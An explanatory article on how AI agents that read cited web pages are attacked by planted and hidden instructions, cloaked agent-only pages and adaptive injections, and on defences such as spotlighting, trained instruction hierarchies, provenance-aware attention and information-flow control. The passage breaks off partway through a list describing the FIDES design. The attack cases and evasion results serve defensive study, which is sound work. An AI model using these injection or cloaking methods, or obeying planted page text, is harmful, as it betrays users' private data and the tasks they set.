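# Defences for AI agents that read cited sources: content provenance, URL and tool restrictions, and checksum or archive verification

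## What can go wrong when an AI agent opens a cited source?

A reader agent is a language model with tools that opens cited sources and uses what it finds there. A cited source is any page or file that a document, a search result or a user points to by its address. Reader agents include chat assistants that search the web, coding tools that look up documentation and research tools that check references. On the network run by Cloudflare, page requests triggered by questions to AI assistants grew more than fifteenfold during 2025, according to company figures that Chen, Canini and colleagues (2026) cite in *Fetch, Read, Reuse*.

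The security problem arises when an agent reads pages written by strangers while it also has access to the user's private files and to tools that send email, run code or spend money. Whoever controls an address can also change what it returns at any time, without notice.

Engineers have four main defences. They can attach a provenance label to each piece of content, recording where it came from, and use ordinary software to decide from the labels which data may reach which action. They can install a URL gate, which checks before each request whether the agent may open a given web address. They can install a tool gate, which checks before each call whether the agent may use a given tool with given arguments. They can also compare the fetched page with an archived copy or with a checksum, a short value that is computed from a file and changes if any byte of the file changes. Each defence works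 against only some failures, so it helps to separate the failures before judging the defences.

### One context for everything

Suppose an analyst has written a report with eighty references and wants to check whether each source supports the sentence that cites it. She gives the job to an agent that can open web addresses, search her files (some of the references are internal documents), and read and send email from her account so it can tell her co-authors about problems.

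The agent works in a loop. The application first combines the developer's standing instructions, a description of each tool and the analyst's request into one text. The model processes this text and produces a tool call, such as a request to open reference 14. Ordinary software carries out the call, converts the page to plain text and appends it to the existing text. The model then processes the combined text and produces the next call. The instructions, the request and the page are all in this single text, which is called the model's context.

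In an indirect prompt injection attack, an AI agent treats text in the content it reads as an instruction. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) traces this weakness to applications that put the developer's instructions and third-party data into a single natural-language context, with no reliable way to keep them separate. The user's request and the text of a cited source therefore reach the model as the same kind of material. The attacker doesn't need access to the user's keyboard, and *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026) notes that the attack may work even without any direct input from the user.

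Converting a web page to plain text can expose an AI agent to instructions that a human visitor would not see. In *Hidden prompts in web content*, Saxton (2026) describes publishing a fake council page about bin collections with six planted instructions for AI readers. Five were hidden from people, for instance in white text on a white background or in an element one pixel wide. The text extractor kept the page's text but ignored the styling that made some of it invisible, so four of the six instructions reached the model as ordinary page text. It dropped only the HTML comment and the description attached to an image. This was one person's test of one page, but most of what it exposed follows from how text extractors work.

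### Six failures

The analyst has three things to lose. Confidentiality means her private data stays with her. Integrity of actions means the agent does what she asked and nothing else. Integrity of the answer means the verdicts in her finished table are right.

**Planted instructions.** The page behind reference 14 may contain text addressed to AI systems, visible or hidden. If the model follows it, the integrity of the agent's actions is lost first, since the agent is now working on somebody else's task. Any further harm depends on that task and the agent's tools. For example, the agent could breach confidentiality by forwarding a draft, or bias its answer by praising the source as instructed. Researchers at the security company Forcepoint also tie the risk to the agent's privileges. In Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*, they describe a browser assistant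 that can only summarise as a low-risk target and an agent that can send email, execute terminal commands or process payments as a high-impact one.

**False content.** A page can also be wrong or fraudulent without containing any instructions. At first, this harms only the integrity of the answer. A recent scam combined false content with hidden instructions. According to SC Media, the security company Zscaler found a website posing as the documentation of a Python software library. Human visitors saw a fraudulent demand for payment in return for a "developer key", and a hidden block gave AI agents the steps for paying. Without the hidden block, the page would still contain false documentation, which an agent could summarise accurately and pass on, and a filter that looks for instructions would not detect it. It is also unclear whose failure this would be. The analyst asked whether the source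 supports her sentence, and a false source may support it, so she would be mistaken to read "supported" as "true".

**Content drift.** A page may change after someone cites it, so the agent compares the analyst's sentence with a text she was not citing. This can make an honest citation look wrong or a bad one look right. The agent may also read a copy that is older than the current page. Chen and colleagues found that the search services of OpenAI, Anthropic and xAI reuse stored copies of pages, so answers can reflect an outdated version for anything from 30 minutes to a day or more. The services also store failures, so an agent built on one of them could report link rot (a cited address no longer returning its page) after the owner has repaired it.

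**Cloaking.** A site can serve agents a different page from the one it serves to people. This can break any of the three properties, depending on what the agents receive. It particularly undermines checking, because if the analyst becomes suspicious and opens reference 14 herself, she sees an ordinary page.

An agent can send private data to an outsider (exfiltration) just by requesting a web page, because the server's owner receives everything written into the requested address. The request breaks confidentiality before the server returns a page.

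**Invented addresses.** If a language model helped draft the reference list, some of the addresses may never have existed, and a stranger can register one and publish a page that fits the citation. The false page can make the agent's answer wrong, and if the page contains instructions, the agent may also act on them.

| Failure | What it breaks | Provenance labels | URL gate | Tool gate | Checksum or archived copy |
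|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Planted instructions | Actions first, then possibly confidentiality or the answer | Can keep page text from steering a sensitive call | Shuts out some hostile sites | Limits the damage | Helps only if someone added the text after the citation |
| False content | The answer | Show whose claim it is, not whether it is true | Helps only with a list of trusted publishers | No help with the answer | No help: a false page can match |
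| Content drift | The answer | Record which copy the agent read, and when | No help | No help | Main defence |
| Cloaking | Any of the three | Mark the text as untrusted whichever version arrives | Little help unless the site is already suspect | Limits the damage | Can expose a mismatch with the page people see |
| Private data in the address | Confidentiality | Can stop labelled data from entering a request | Main defence | Can withhold the private files while the agent browses | No help |
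| Invented address | The answer, then possibly actions | Record that the address came from a draft, not from a search | Main defence | Limits the damage | No older copy exists, which is a warning in itself |

The row for false content lists the least protection. A provenance label can help the analyst identify the publisher, but she must judge the publisher's reliability herself.

### Pages that only agents see

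Spammers have long used cloaking, which means showing search engines' crawlers one page and human visitors another. Phishing sites use the same trick to hide from security scanners. *A Whole New World* (Zychlinski, 2025) applies it to AI agents and calls the result a parallel-poisoned web. The server first looks for signs that a visitor is an agent: a declared name, traces of browser-automation software, a network address belonging to a cloud provider, or unnaturally regular behaviour. If it finds them, it returns a hostile version of the page. Other visitors, including known security crawlers, get the harmless version.

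An attacker's server can easily recognise some agents. Chen and colleagues logged every request to websites they ran and found that the fetchers of OpenAI and Anthropic identify themselves as ChatGPT-User and Claude-User, so a simple server rule can single them out. xAI's fetcher sends the identifier of an ordinary browser, but it makes a median of six requests per question, many of them in parallel, which is unlike a person reading a page. Other agents are harder to recognise. *FP-Agent (2026)*, a study of browsing agents, notes that many of them send generic browser identifiers and that not all declare themselves.

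Generic identifiers may not protect agents for long. *Whose Agent Are You?* (2026) describes a classifier that combines request timing, details of the encrypted connection, HTTP headers and behaviour on the page. It separated agents, crawlers and humans with 100% accuracy. The test covered only six agent frameworks visiting the researchers' own test site, so the result is weak evidence about other frameworks, but it suggests that changing a browser's name does little to disguise an agent. *Identifying AI Web Scrapers Using Canary Tokens* (2026) traced chatbots by planting unique strings on websites, and found that many seem to take their text from search-engine results without visiting the site. This gives them some protection, since an attacker would presumably have to deceive the search engine first.

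Zychlinski ran a small experiment of his own. He built an internal website with a page of software documentation and a server script that detects agents. When an agent arrived, the server withheld the documentation and returned a demand that the agent authenticate with the value of a secret key stored on the user's machine. He sent the coding tool Cursor to the site, running Claude 4 Sonnet, GPT-5 Fast and Gemini 2.5 Pro in turn. He reports that the attack succeeded with all three models.

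Zychlinski's experiment showed that a server can send agents a different page from the one people see, and that three capable models of 2025, running inside one coding tool with access to secrets, gave up a key when a page demanded it. The finding is narrow. Zychlinski gives no number of trials and ran no comparison in which people and agents received the same page, so the experiment cannot show how much the cloaking contributed. It probably contributed nothing to the models' compliance, since a model cannot see what other visitors receive. Cloaking helps an attacker by keeping people and scanners from noticing the attack. Because the site was internal, the experiment also does not show whether anyone does this on the public web. Zychlinski lists a large-scale search for agent-targeted cloaking as future work.

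One remedy he proposes is for agents to randomise their fingerprints and blend in with human traffic. But publishers who want to set rules for AI visitors need those visitors to identify themselves, and an agent that does so is the easiest to target with cloaked pages. It is hard to see how an agent could both satisfy publishers and avoid cloaking with one identity.

A mismatch between the agent's text and the visible page can have an innocent cause, such as the page's length or its use of JavaScript. Chen and colleagues found that no service they tested reads content that appears only through JavaScript, and that xAI's service reads only the first 0.5 MB of a page. They also found that OpenAI, Anthropic and xAI reuse a copy of a page fetched for one user to answer another user's question, so a cloaked page that a server delivers once could affect several people's answers.

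### How common are planted instructions?

The best count so far comes from Khodayari and colleagues. They searched 1.2 billion addresses on 24.8 million hosts, about half of the October 2025 release of Common Crawl, a large public archive of web pages. Running a detection model over so much text would have cost too much, so they searched for fixed phrases. They collected known injection wordings from earlier research and industry reports, then swapped verbs and objects to generate variants, for a total of 3,963 search strings. These matched 27,860 times. Tutorials and news articles about prompt injection contain the same phrases, so two reviewers grouped and inspected the matches, keeping only text that functions as an instruction to a machine.

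They kept 12,075 instances on 9,676 pages and 285 hosts, or roughly eight pages in every million. The analyst's eighty references aren't a random sample of the crawl, but if they were, the chance that any of them carried a planted instruction would be under one in a thousand. Her actual risk could be lower because injection rates are lower among the most popular sites, or higher because an attacker who wants reference-checking agents to visit a page will work to get it cited.

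To cover a wider variety of injections, the researchers added results from Censys and Shodan, two search engines for internet-connected servers, for a total of 15,387 instances on 11,722 pages and 2,042 hosts. Most are more a nuisance than an attack. One instruction can count under several aims. Of the instances, 8,469 are meant to make the model produce garbage, such as strings of random numbers. Another 4,093 are meant to protect personal information or copyrighted text from reuse, and 3,096 are meant to expose bots, for example by getting an AI system to include a tell-tale word in a form. Only 13 are meant to extract data, and 157 contain destructive or command-like payloads.

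The category that matters most to a reference checker is reputation manipulation, with 1,521 instances. Of these, 542 are attempts to force the model to treat the page as an authoritative source and cite it, although all 542 are on two hosts.

In the Common Crawl part of the data, the site's own operator placed 80.6% of the instructions. Other people placed the rest through job advertisements, marketplace listings and comments, so a URL gate that trusts a whole host will let some strangers' text through. The researchers also looked for older copies of the affected pages in the Internet Archive. They found a copy from about a year earlier for 8,620 pages, and 5,672 of those copies already contained an injection. The researchers stress this persistence, but the other nearly 3,000 pages are just as interesting for anyone who follows citations. The search detected no injection in their archived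 copies, so an author could have cited any of them in good faith about a year before the live page was found to contain one.

Khodayari and colleagues tested whether the planted instructions work. They sampled 100 distinct instructions and gave the pages containing them, in four formats, to 13 models to summarise, for 5,200 runs in all. When the page was converted to plain text, models followed the planted instruction in 3.9% of runs, and small models did so in 8%. With a structured snapshot of the rendered page, which preserves clues about what is visible, the overall rate fell to 1.1%. The rate for raw HTML was also 1.1%, but a fifth of those runs ended in errors, mostly because the page was too long for the model, so that figure makes raw HTML look safer than it is. In six cases, a model flagged the malicious instruction but still followed it.

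These rates come from a summarising task with no tools, so they do not measure how often a full agent would go on to act. Zscaler's test comes closer, because it gave the fake Python documentation to an agent that could browse and make cryptocurrency payments. SC Media reports that 4 of the 26 models tested, two versions of Llama 3 and two of Gemini, made the payment. The scammer's wallet had received some money, but never the amount the page demanded, so it is unclear whether the page ever led to a payment. Infosecurity Magazine's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* adds that the attackers had manipulated search rankings to push their sites up the results, where agents would be more likely to find them, an effort that a count of pages does not measure.

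The main evidence on the trend comes from *AI threats in the wild* (2026). Brunner, Liu and Pande of Google searched several monthly releases of Common Crawl, each with 2 to 3 billion pages, for popular injection phrases. Gemini then classified the intent of each candidate, and people reviewed the remaining candidates. Much of what they found was pranks, attempts to promote a business, requests to leave the site alone, or website owners' guidance on how to summarise their pages. The malicious category, which covers data theft and destruction, grew by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026.

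That widely quoted percentage is weaker evidence than it seems. The report gives no absolute counts, so the rise could be from 50 pages to 66 or from 5,000 to 6,600. The comparison also covers only a few months and depends on a list of known phrases. Google describes the attacks as unsophisticated, mostly experiments or pranks by individual site owners, with little sign of the advanced exfiltration methods that researchers published in 2025. It expects both scale and sophistication to grow, because agents are becoming more valuable targets and attackers can now automate their work.

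Unit 42, the research group of the security vendor Palo Alto Networks, reports more malicious attacks in *Fooling AI Agents* (2026). Destroying data accounts for 14.2% of the attackers' aims it recorded, second to producing irrelevant output at 28.6%. Attackers most often delivered instructions in visible text (37.8%), whereas Khodayari and colleagues found that about 87% of their instances were hidden from users. Differences between the samples probably explain most of this gap. Unit 42's detections lean towards malicious sites, and more than half of the academic study's instances are in HTTP headers, which browsers never display. Unit 42 also documents a scam advertisement with 24 separate injection attempts on one page, aimed at automated ad reviewers, but says it knows of no confirmed case in which such an attack worked on a deployed reviewer.

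All of these counts are lower bounds. A phrase search misses unfamiliar wordings, instructions in other languages and text inside images, and Common Crawl leaves out most social media. Common Crawl also almost inevitably misses cloaking, because a site that shows its hostile page only to AI agents would serve the archive's crawler the clean one.

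## Does marking web text as untrusted stop a model from obeying it?

Planted instructions seem to be rare, but an agent that opens enough pages will eventually meet one, and its developer wants it to carry on with the user's task anyway. One defence is to tell the model which part of its context came from an untrusted source. The application can identify and mark that text without examining it, because it fetched the page itself. Developers can also train the model to give marked text less authority, or build the mark into the model's internal calculations. All of these defences depend on the model actually giving marked text less authority. They often work against attacks written without them in mind, but most of those that outsiders have seriously tried to break have failed.

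Researchers judge these defences by attack success rate, the share of attack attempts in which the attacker achieves their goal, and utility, the share of the user's tasks that the agent completes correctly. Both matter because an agent that reads nothing would never obey a planted instruction but would also fail any task that requires reading.

### Cleaning and marking the text

The most basic defence removes text that a person would not see. Ordinary software can do this by working from the page as a browser displays it. The model never receives the hidden text, so the defence doesn't depend on the model treating marked text as untrusted. Saxton's fake council page, which contained hidden instructions, shows why this is worth doing. But a visibility filter doesn't remove instructions written in plain view, which was the most common method in Unit 42's sample. Pages also hide text for legitimate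 reasons, such as in a section that opens on a click, so a strict filter removes some evidence that a reference checker could use.

A developer can add a warning not to follow instructions in a document, or put delimiters (special symbols) before and after its text. Hines, Lopez and colleagues at Microsoft tested both in *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting* (2024). They generated 1,000 documents containing text that urged the model to drop its task and return a single keyword. Without a defence, the attack worked on GPT-3.5-Turbo about 60% of the time. A warning alone barely changed that rate, and a warning with delimiters cut it by about half. They still advise against delimiters, because an attacker who learns the developer's instructions can insert delimiters too, making the attack text appear to lie outside the untrusted block.

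They proposed spotlighting, a family of three ways to present untrusted text so that the model can tell it from everything else:

| Method | What the model receives |
|---|---|
| None | `The bridge opened in 1932.` |
| Delimiting | `<<The bridge opened in 1932.>>` |
| Datamarking | `The^bridge^opened^in^1932.` |
| Encoding (base64) | `VGhlIGJyaWRnZSBvcGVuZWQgaW4gMTkzMi4=` |

Datamarking replaces every space with a special character, so the mark runs through the whole document and an attacker has no boundary to fake. Encoding rewrites the text in a standard code that a capable model can decode as it works. In both cases, the developer explains the transformation to the model and tells it not to follow instructions in the transformed text.

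Datamarking cut the attack success rate for GPT-3.5-Turbo from roughly half to 3.1% when it summarised documents and 8% when it answered questions about them. For GPT-4, the rate on questions fell to 1%. Encoding lowered GPT-3.5-Turbo's rates further, to 0% on summaries and 1.8% on questions, but the model made decoding mistakes and became much worse at its ordinary tasks. GPT-4 handled encoded text well. The tests used 2023 models and an attack that only tried to make them output one word.

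Google's experience suggests that much of spotlighting's protection may come from garbling the attack, and rather little from telling the model where the text came from, as its inventors intended. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) describes a version in which software inserts a marker into untrusted emails every eight characters. Google's experiments showed that this helps mainly by disrupting tokenisation, the splitting of text into the short chunks that a model processes. The markers break up the attack's trigger words, so the model is less likely to treat them as an instruction. An attacker may therefore only need to find a wording that still works when it is broken up.

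Delimiters also let many injections through on newer models. In *Defense Against Indirect Prompt Injection via Tool Result Parsing*, Yu, Cheng and Liu (2026) used AgentDojo, a set of 97 tasks in banking, travel, team chat and office work, where some tool results contain injections. Against AgentDojo's most effective ready-made attack, delimiters lowered the success rate only from 26.5% to 23.3% on gpt-oss-120b and from 29.8% to 25.1% on Qwen3-32B. The drop was larger on Llama-3.1-70B, from 22.2% to 13.2%. Repeating the user's request after the fetched text, known as sandwiching, left success rates between 12% and 17%. Yu and colleagues consider both methods unusable in practice.

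### Training a model to rank its sources

Marking web text as untrusted does little unless the model has been trained to respect the marking. *The Instruction Hierarchy* (2024) compares the usual situation to an operating system that runs every program, including a stranger's, with full privileges. It proposes training the model to follow the instruction from the more privileged source when two instructions conflict. According to *Training LLMs to Enforce Multi-Level Instruction Hierarchies via Gravity-Weighted Direct Preference Optimization* (2026), the original work used three levels and trained GPT-3.5 on synthetic conflicts between them. The 2026 paper extends the scheme to five levels and penalises violations more heavily when they override a higher level.

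*When Context Gets Root* (2026) points out that ordinary training data also teaches models to trust text by its role, because the assistant in the chat logs used for training almost always follows the developer's instructions. If an attacker forges a privileged label inside a tool result, or careless software puts page text under the wrong role, the training that should limit hostile text's influence increases it instead.

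Two other methods, StruQ and SecAlign, teach a model the narrower skill of separating a request from the data it concerns. StruQ marks the data with its own separator and fine-tunes the model on examples where the data contains instructions and the correct answer ignores them. SecAlign pairs two responses to an input that contains an injected instruction, one that answers the original request and one that obeys the injection, and training makes the first more likely.

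Zhang, Huang and Gu (2026), in *Origin Is All You Need*, compared several of these methods on one small model, Llama-3-8B. The table shows attack success rates in per cent. SEP is a set of 4,375 examples held out from the paper's own training data. The other three sets cover different tasks and styles of injection. PI-Attack and DataSentinel mostly involve classifying text, and Math-Tutor involves solving problems.

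| Defence on Llama-3-8B | SEP | PI-Attack | DataSentinel | Math-Tutor |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 32.5 | 21.3 | 24.1 | 17.2 |
| Warning | 30.9 | 16.1 | 20.7 | 19.9 |
| Delimiters | 11.7 | 9.0 | 22.4 | 4.1 |
| SecAlign | 2.0 | 0.0 | 6.9 | 0.0 |
| Training by Zhang and colleagues, no origin signal | 0.8 | 2.3 | 8.6 | 0.3 |
| The same training with an origin signal | 0.7 | 0.0 | 0.0 | 0.0 |

On these fixed attacks, training clearly works better than a warning or a delimiter. The DataSentinel column is weaker evidence than the others because that set has only 178 examples.

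### An origin signal with every token

The last row of the table comes from changing the model itself. Zhang and colleagues call the modified model a provenance-aware transformer. The application gives each token (a short chunk of text) a number for its origin: 0 for the developer's instructions, 1 for the model's own output, 2 for the user and trusted data, and 3 for untrusted sources. The model adds a learned vector for that number to the token's ordinary vector, so information about the token's origin is present from the first layer.

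The more important change is in attention, the operation by which a model weighs earlier tokens when it processes a new one. Normally the score between token $i$ and an earlier token $j$ comes from two vectors, $q_i$ and $k_j$, that the model computes from the tokens. Zhang and colleagues add a term that depends only on the two origins, $r_i$ and $r_j$:

$$a_{ij} = \frac{q_i \cdot k_j}{\sqrt{d_k}} + B_{r_i, r_j}$$

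Here $d_k$ is the number of entries in each vector. When training for injection resistance begins, $B$ is a large negative number, $-\delta$, where the model's own tokens or the user's tokens attend to untrusted ones, and zero everywhere else. A token's weight is proportional to $e^{a_{ij}}$, so the extra term multiplies an untrusted token's weight by $e^{-\delta}$ before the weights are rescaled to sum to one. If $\delta$ were 10, the factor would be about 1/22,000.

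Training has two stages. The first uses 105,000 general examples with origin numbers attached to restore the ordinary skills of the modified model. The second uses 60,200 examples, 24,079 of which contain an injection, to teach it to ignore origin 3. Results on Qwen2.5-7B, Mistral-7B and the much smaller SmolLM2-360M resemble those on Llama-3-8B. The difference from plain training is most striking on Mistral-7B, where 17.8% of the PI-Attack injections succeed without the origin signal and 0.03% succeed with it.

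The attention term provides nearly all of the protection. When Zhang and colleagues switched it off in the finished Llama model, between 68% and 90% of attacks succeeded, far more than on the original model before any training.

These results are limited evidence about reading web pages, because the labels in the examples already showed the model where the attack was. To build a training example, Zhang and colleagues inserted an injection into an ordinary document and gave origin 3 to the injection alone. The document around it kept origin 2, as trusted data. The held-out examples follow the same pattern. An application that has just fetched a cited source doesn't know which parts of it are an attack, and the simple policy in the paper is to give the entire page origin 3. The model would then suppress the evidence along with the attack. Zhang and colleagues acknowledge that legitimate content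 with this label is also suppressed, and suggest finer divisions of trust. Their utility test consists of 805 general requests and does not measure how well the model uses a page labelled as untrusted. In that test, a judge model preferred the modified Llama's answers to the original's 48.8% of the time, which is about level. The modified Mistral did worse, at 42.7%.

### Letting less of the page through

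A developer can also reduce the amount of hostile text that needs a mark. Yu and colleagues observe that tools return more than an agent needs. Before each tool call, their method has the model specify what data it expects, in what format, and within what limits. When the result arrives, the model extracts only data that fits. If the analyst's agent needs a publication year from reference 14, it should receive only four digits, because a paragraph of instructions doesn't fit the format of a year.

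A second module handles tasks that need whole passages. It shows the text to the model and checks whether the model tries to call a tool. If it does, the module prompts the model to remove the words responsible. With both modules in place, AgentDojo's strongest ready-made attack succeeded in 0.5% of cases on gpt-oss-120b, 0.1% on Qwen3-32B and none on Llama-3.1-70B.

The models completed considerably fewer tasks with the defence, even when there was no attack. Qwen3-32B completed 83.5% of its tasks undefended and 45.4% with both modules, gpt-oss-120b 61.9% and 48.5%, and Llama 49.5% and 28.9%. With extraction alone, Qwen completed 63.9%, and an average of 0.8% of attacks got through. Yu and colleagues tested only fixed attacks, and the model that does the filtering also has to read the hostile text. They acknowledge that a false value in the right format passes. For example, a page could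 give an attacker's email address as a doctor's, so that the agent sends the payment to the wrong person. A reference checker has the same problem with a false year. A more basic problem is that a checker usually needs a page's prose to decide whether the page supports a sentence, so the extraction step could seldom discard much.

*Prismata* (Villa, Tan and colleagues, 2026), a UC Berkeley project, divides a web page according to who wrote each part. It uses the page's tree of nested elements, in which a reviews section, for example, contains a review, which contains a reply button. For each button, link or form field, a labelling model receives the user's task, the element's text and the chain of elements that enclose it, and decides whether the task requires that element. An injection elsewhere on the page cannot affect this decision, because the labelling model never receives it.

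A separate pass works down from the top of the page's element tree and labels each element by author: the site's developer, a user, a hosted party such as a marketplace seller, or an outside party such as an advertiser. It fixes each label before revealing the elements below, and no element can have more trust than the one that encloses it. For example, once a section has been labelled from its heading, "Customer reviews", nothing a reviewer writes there can raise its trust. Ordinary code then deletes strangers' text that the task does not need, leaves the rest for reading only, and rejects any click on an element outside the task.

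This design relies on pages having a helpful structure, so Villa and colleagues examined 5,664 pages. Of the 90,408 pieces of untrusted content they found, 1.2% enclosed something the agent could click or fill in, and 94 (about 0.1%) did so without an earlier clue such as a heading. Language models annotated the pages, so these figures are estimates, but they are low enough to leave a large margin for error.

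They then tested an agent running gpt-5.4-mini against three kinds of hostile pop-up in WebArena, a set of realistic copies of a shop, a forum and other sites. An attack succeeded if the agent interacted with the planted content, for instance by clicking its link. The defence cut the average attack success rate from 85.5% to 0.7% and raised task completion under attack from 4.5% to 23.0%. Without attacks, task completion fell from 29.9% to 26.6%, a drop of about one ninth. Model fees for a run of 20 tasks rose by almost half, even with reuse of earlier labels.

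Prismata fits a shopping agent better than a reference checker. It assumes an honest site on which strangers have posted, and trusts the developer's text. In the web-wide count by Khodayari and colleagues, however, site operators had placed about four fifths of the instructions. The safety argument also assumes that the agent can act only through the browser, but the analyst's agent can also send email. When the task requires strangers' text, the agent still reads it, so a fake review can mislead an agent comparing reviews. Villa and colleagues leave that case to the model's reasoning.

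### When the attacker adapts

Most of the figures above come from attacks that take no account of the defence. A real attacker can study the defence and revise the attack after each attempt. An adaptive attack is one designed or optimised against the particular defence being tested. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) ran adaptive attacks against 12 published defences, most of which had attack success rates near zero in their original evaluations. The team included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind.

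Their main automated method is a search in which a language model writes an attack, the defended agent is tested against it, and another model scores how close the attack came to its goal. The first model uses the score and the agent's output to write the next attempt, up to a total of 800. The test covered 80 pairs of user and attacker tasks from AgentDojo. The table shows the success rate of one fixed attack, then that of the search.

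| Model | No added defence | Spotlighting | Sandwiching |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 30% → 100% | 28% → 99% | 21% → 95% |
| GPT-5 Mini | 0% → 75% | 0% → 47% | 0% → 69% |
| Llama-3.3 70B | 35% → 100% | 28% → 99% | 25% → 100% |
| Meta SecAlign 70B | 5% → 96% | 1% → 99% | 4% → 99% |

The median successful search against Gemini with spotlighting needed only 14 attempts. Against Meta SecAlign, a later model from the SecAlign line, the search raised the attack success rate on AgentDojo from a reported 2% to 96%. Nasr and colleagues used reinforcement learning to train a model to attack StruQ, and it succeeded in every case they tried. Most successful attacks on the trained defences imitated instructions from the system's developer, although the training was supposed to stop models from mistaking untrusted text for such instructions.

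Separate detectors, which screen text for injections before the model receives it, did little better. The search succeeded more than 90% of the time against three of the four detectors. Against the fourth, PIGuard, it succeeded 71% of the time on Gemini. PIGuard also cut Gemini's utility from 74% to 39%.

Many successful texts presented the attacker's task as a step that the user's task required. An instruction hierarchy handles such texts poorly because it settles conflicts between instructions, and these texts are written so that no conflict appears. This also explains why sandwiching fails, since reminding the model of the user's task does not help if the model already treats the attacker's task as part of it.

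GPT-5 Mini is the exception in the table. The fixed attack never worked on it, and spotlighting reduced the search's success from 75% to 47%. Nasr and colleagues believe a larger budget would close the gap, but they did not show it. They describe the spotlighting they tested as using delimiters, the variant that Hines and colleagues had advised against, so the table does not directly measure datamarking or encoding. Expecting much from either would be optimistic, because human attackers in a competition with over 500 participants beat all 29 setups, defended and undefended, on which the researchers compared them with the search.

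In 2026, defenders are running adaptive tests of their own, which partly answers this criticism. Zhang and colleagues gave attackers full access to their modified model's weights. A standard attack that uses the model's gradients to optimise a string of tokens succeeded 1.4% of the time, compared with 50.7% on the undefended model. The paper reports a second attack's success rate as 1.6% in one place and 0.9% in another, compared with about 48% on the undefended model. These results are evidence that the defence works against such attacks, and the reason is that the application assigns the origin number, so an attacker can't change it by rewording the text. But both attacks are existing algorithms, and Nasr and colleagues found gradient methods unreliable against language models and recommend searching over ordinary text instead. Nobody has yet reported testing this design with such a search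 or with a competition in which people try to break it.

Villa and colleagues tried adaptive versions of their pop-ups on 20 tasks. The attacks succeeded 65% to 100% of the time without Prismata and never with it. With only 20 tries per attack, the true success rate for any one attack could still be as high as about 14%, at 95% confidence. They also ran a set of 21 tests called WASP, but only one attack succeeded against the undefended agent, which left little for a defence to prevent.

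### Why a mark gives only a probability

A language model computes a probability for each possible next token from everything in its context, and the mark is one more input to that computation. No separate step checks the mark and blocks instructions in the marked text. Training can make the model unlikely to obey marked text that resembles the training examples, but it does not guarantee this for every text an attacker could write. A test on a fixed set of attacks estimates the average success rate over that set, while security depends on the most effective text an attacker can find. This difference explains the gap between the 1% and 99% attack success rates for Meta SecAlign with spotlighting.

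If each attempt has a 1% chance of success, independent of the others, the chance of at least one success in 100 attempts is $1 - 0.99^{100}$, or about 63%. An attacker with a popular page gets many attempts because many agents visit it, and he can test the attack beforehand on his own copy of the same product.

Prismata's last step differs because code enforces it. Once the code has disabled a button, no wording on the page can make the click go through, although a language model still chose which buttons to disable. Software outside the model can enforce limits on data and tools in a similar way.

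A stronger mark cannot solve the problem by itself, as the provenance-aware transformer illustrates. Its penalty $\delta$ is finite, so untrusted words keep a little influence. An infinite penalty would remove their direct influence, but it would also make fetching the page pointless. The analyst needs the text of reference 14 to affect the agent's verdict, and a planted instruction reaches the model by the same route as the evidence.

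## Can software outside the model track where each value came from?

Ordinary software runs every tool on the model's behalf, so a program between the model and the tools can record where data came from and refuse a call that breaks a rule. Engineers call this information-flow control, and its basic ideas date from the 1970s. In published tests, the best designs stop almost every planted instruction that aims at a harmful action, whatever its wording. They also refuse some legitimate tasks, and they do very little to stop a false page from corrupting an answer.

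Microsoft's *information flow control moving toward secure autonomous agents* argues that designers should assume a model's mistake or a prompt injection can trigger anything that a user's request can. The protection therefore has to come from software outside the model that decides which calls to carry out.

### Labels and the rule for combining them

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) use labels with two parts in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*. The integrity part marks a piece of data as trusted or untrusted, and the confidentiality part lists who may read it. They note that a simpler system could replace the list of readers with two levels, public and secret.

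When software combines several pieces of data, the result takes the most restrictive label. If $y$ is computed from $x_1, \dots, x_n$, with integrity $I$ and set of permitted readers $R$, then

$$I(y) = \begin{cases} \text{trusted} & \text{if every } I(x_k) \text{ is trusted} \\ \text{untrusted} & \text{otherwise} \end{cases} \qquad R(y) = R(x_1) \cap \dots \cap R(x_n)$$

So one untrusted ingredient makes the result untrusted, and only people who may read every ingredient may read the result.

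A language model makes this harder, because software cannot see which words in the context influenced the model's output. The cautious solution is to treat the whole context $C$ as an ingredient of everything the model writes, including the tool calls it proposes. A strict rule for sending an email to address $a$ is then

$$\text{allow the email to } a \iff I(C) = \text{trusted} \ \text{ and } \ a \in R(C)$$

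Suppose the page behind reference 14 gives an email address for corrections. After reading the page, the analyst's agent proposes to send that address a passage from her unpublished draft. The context contains three things:

| In the context | Integrity | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| The analyst's request | Trusted | Anyone |
| Her unpublished draft | Trusted | The analyst and her co-authors |
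| The page behind reference 14 | Untrusted | Anyone |
| Combined label | Untrusted | The analyst and her co-authors |

The email fails both conditions because the page has made the context untrusted and the address does not belong to someone allowed to read the draft. The program never interprets the page's text, so no wording on the page can change the outcome.

The same rule also blocks an email the analyst wants, such as one telling a co-author that reference 14 looks doubtful. The co-author is a permitted reader, but the context is still untrusted. Once the agent has read its first web page, it can't send email at all. The designs below differ mostly in how they avoid this.

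### Keeping the page away from the planner

One solution is to keep untrusted text out of the context that produces tool calls. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) traces this to the Dual LLM pattern, which the programmer Simon Willison proposed in 2023. A planning model calls the tools, while a second, quarantined model with no tools reads the untrusted text. Software stores the text in a named variable, which the planner can pass on without seeing its contents.

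Google DeepMind's CaMeL (2025) implements this pattern. According to *ROPE* (Ma, Xiao and colleagues, 2026), it turns the user's request into a program and attaches a record of its source to each value. For the analyst, such a program might open each address in her list, have the quarantined model compare the page with her sentence, store the verdict and email the finished table to her co-authors. Because the program exists before the agent opens any page, a page can't add a step to it, but it can supply a value that a later step uses. This is why each value carries its source. If the analyst had asked the agent to email the contact named on each page, the software could check where the email address came from before sending.

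FIDES, from Costa and colleagues at Microsoft, doesn't need the whole program in advance. Its planner chooses one step at a time, and the software around it does the following:

1. A tool returns a result, and FIDES labels it.
2. If adding the result to the planner's context would make the context's label more restrictive, FIDES stores the text in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. Other results go into the context as usual.
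3. When the planner uses the variable in a tool call, FIDES substitutes the stored text and looks up its label.
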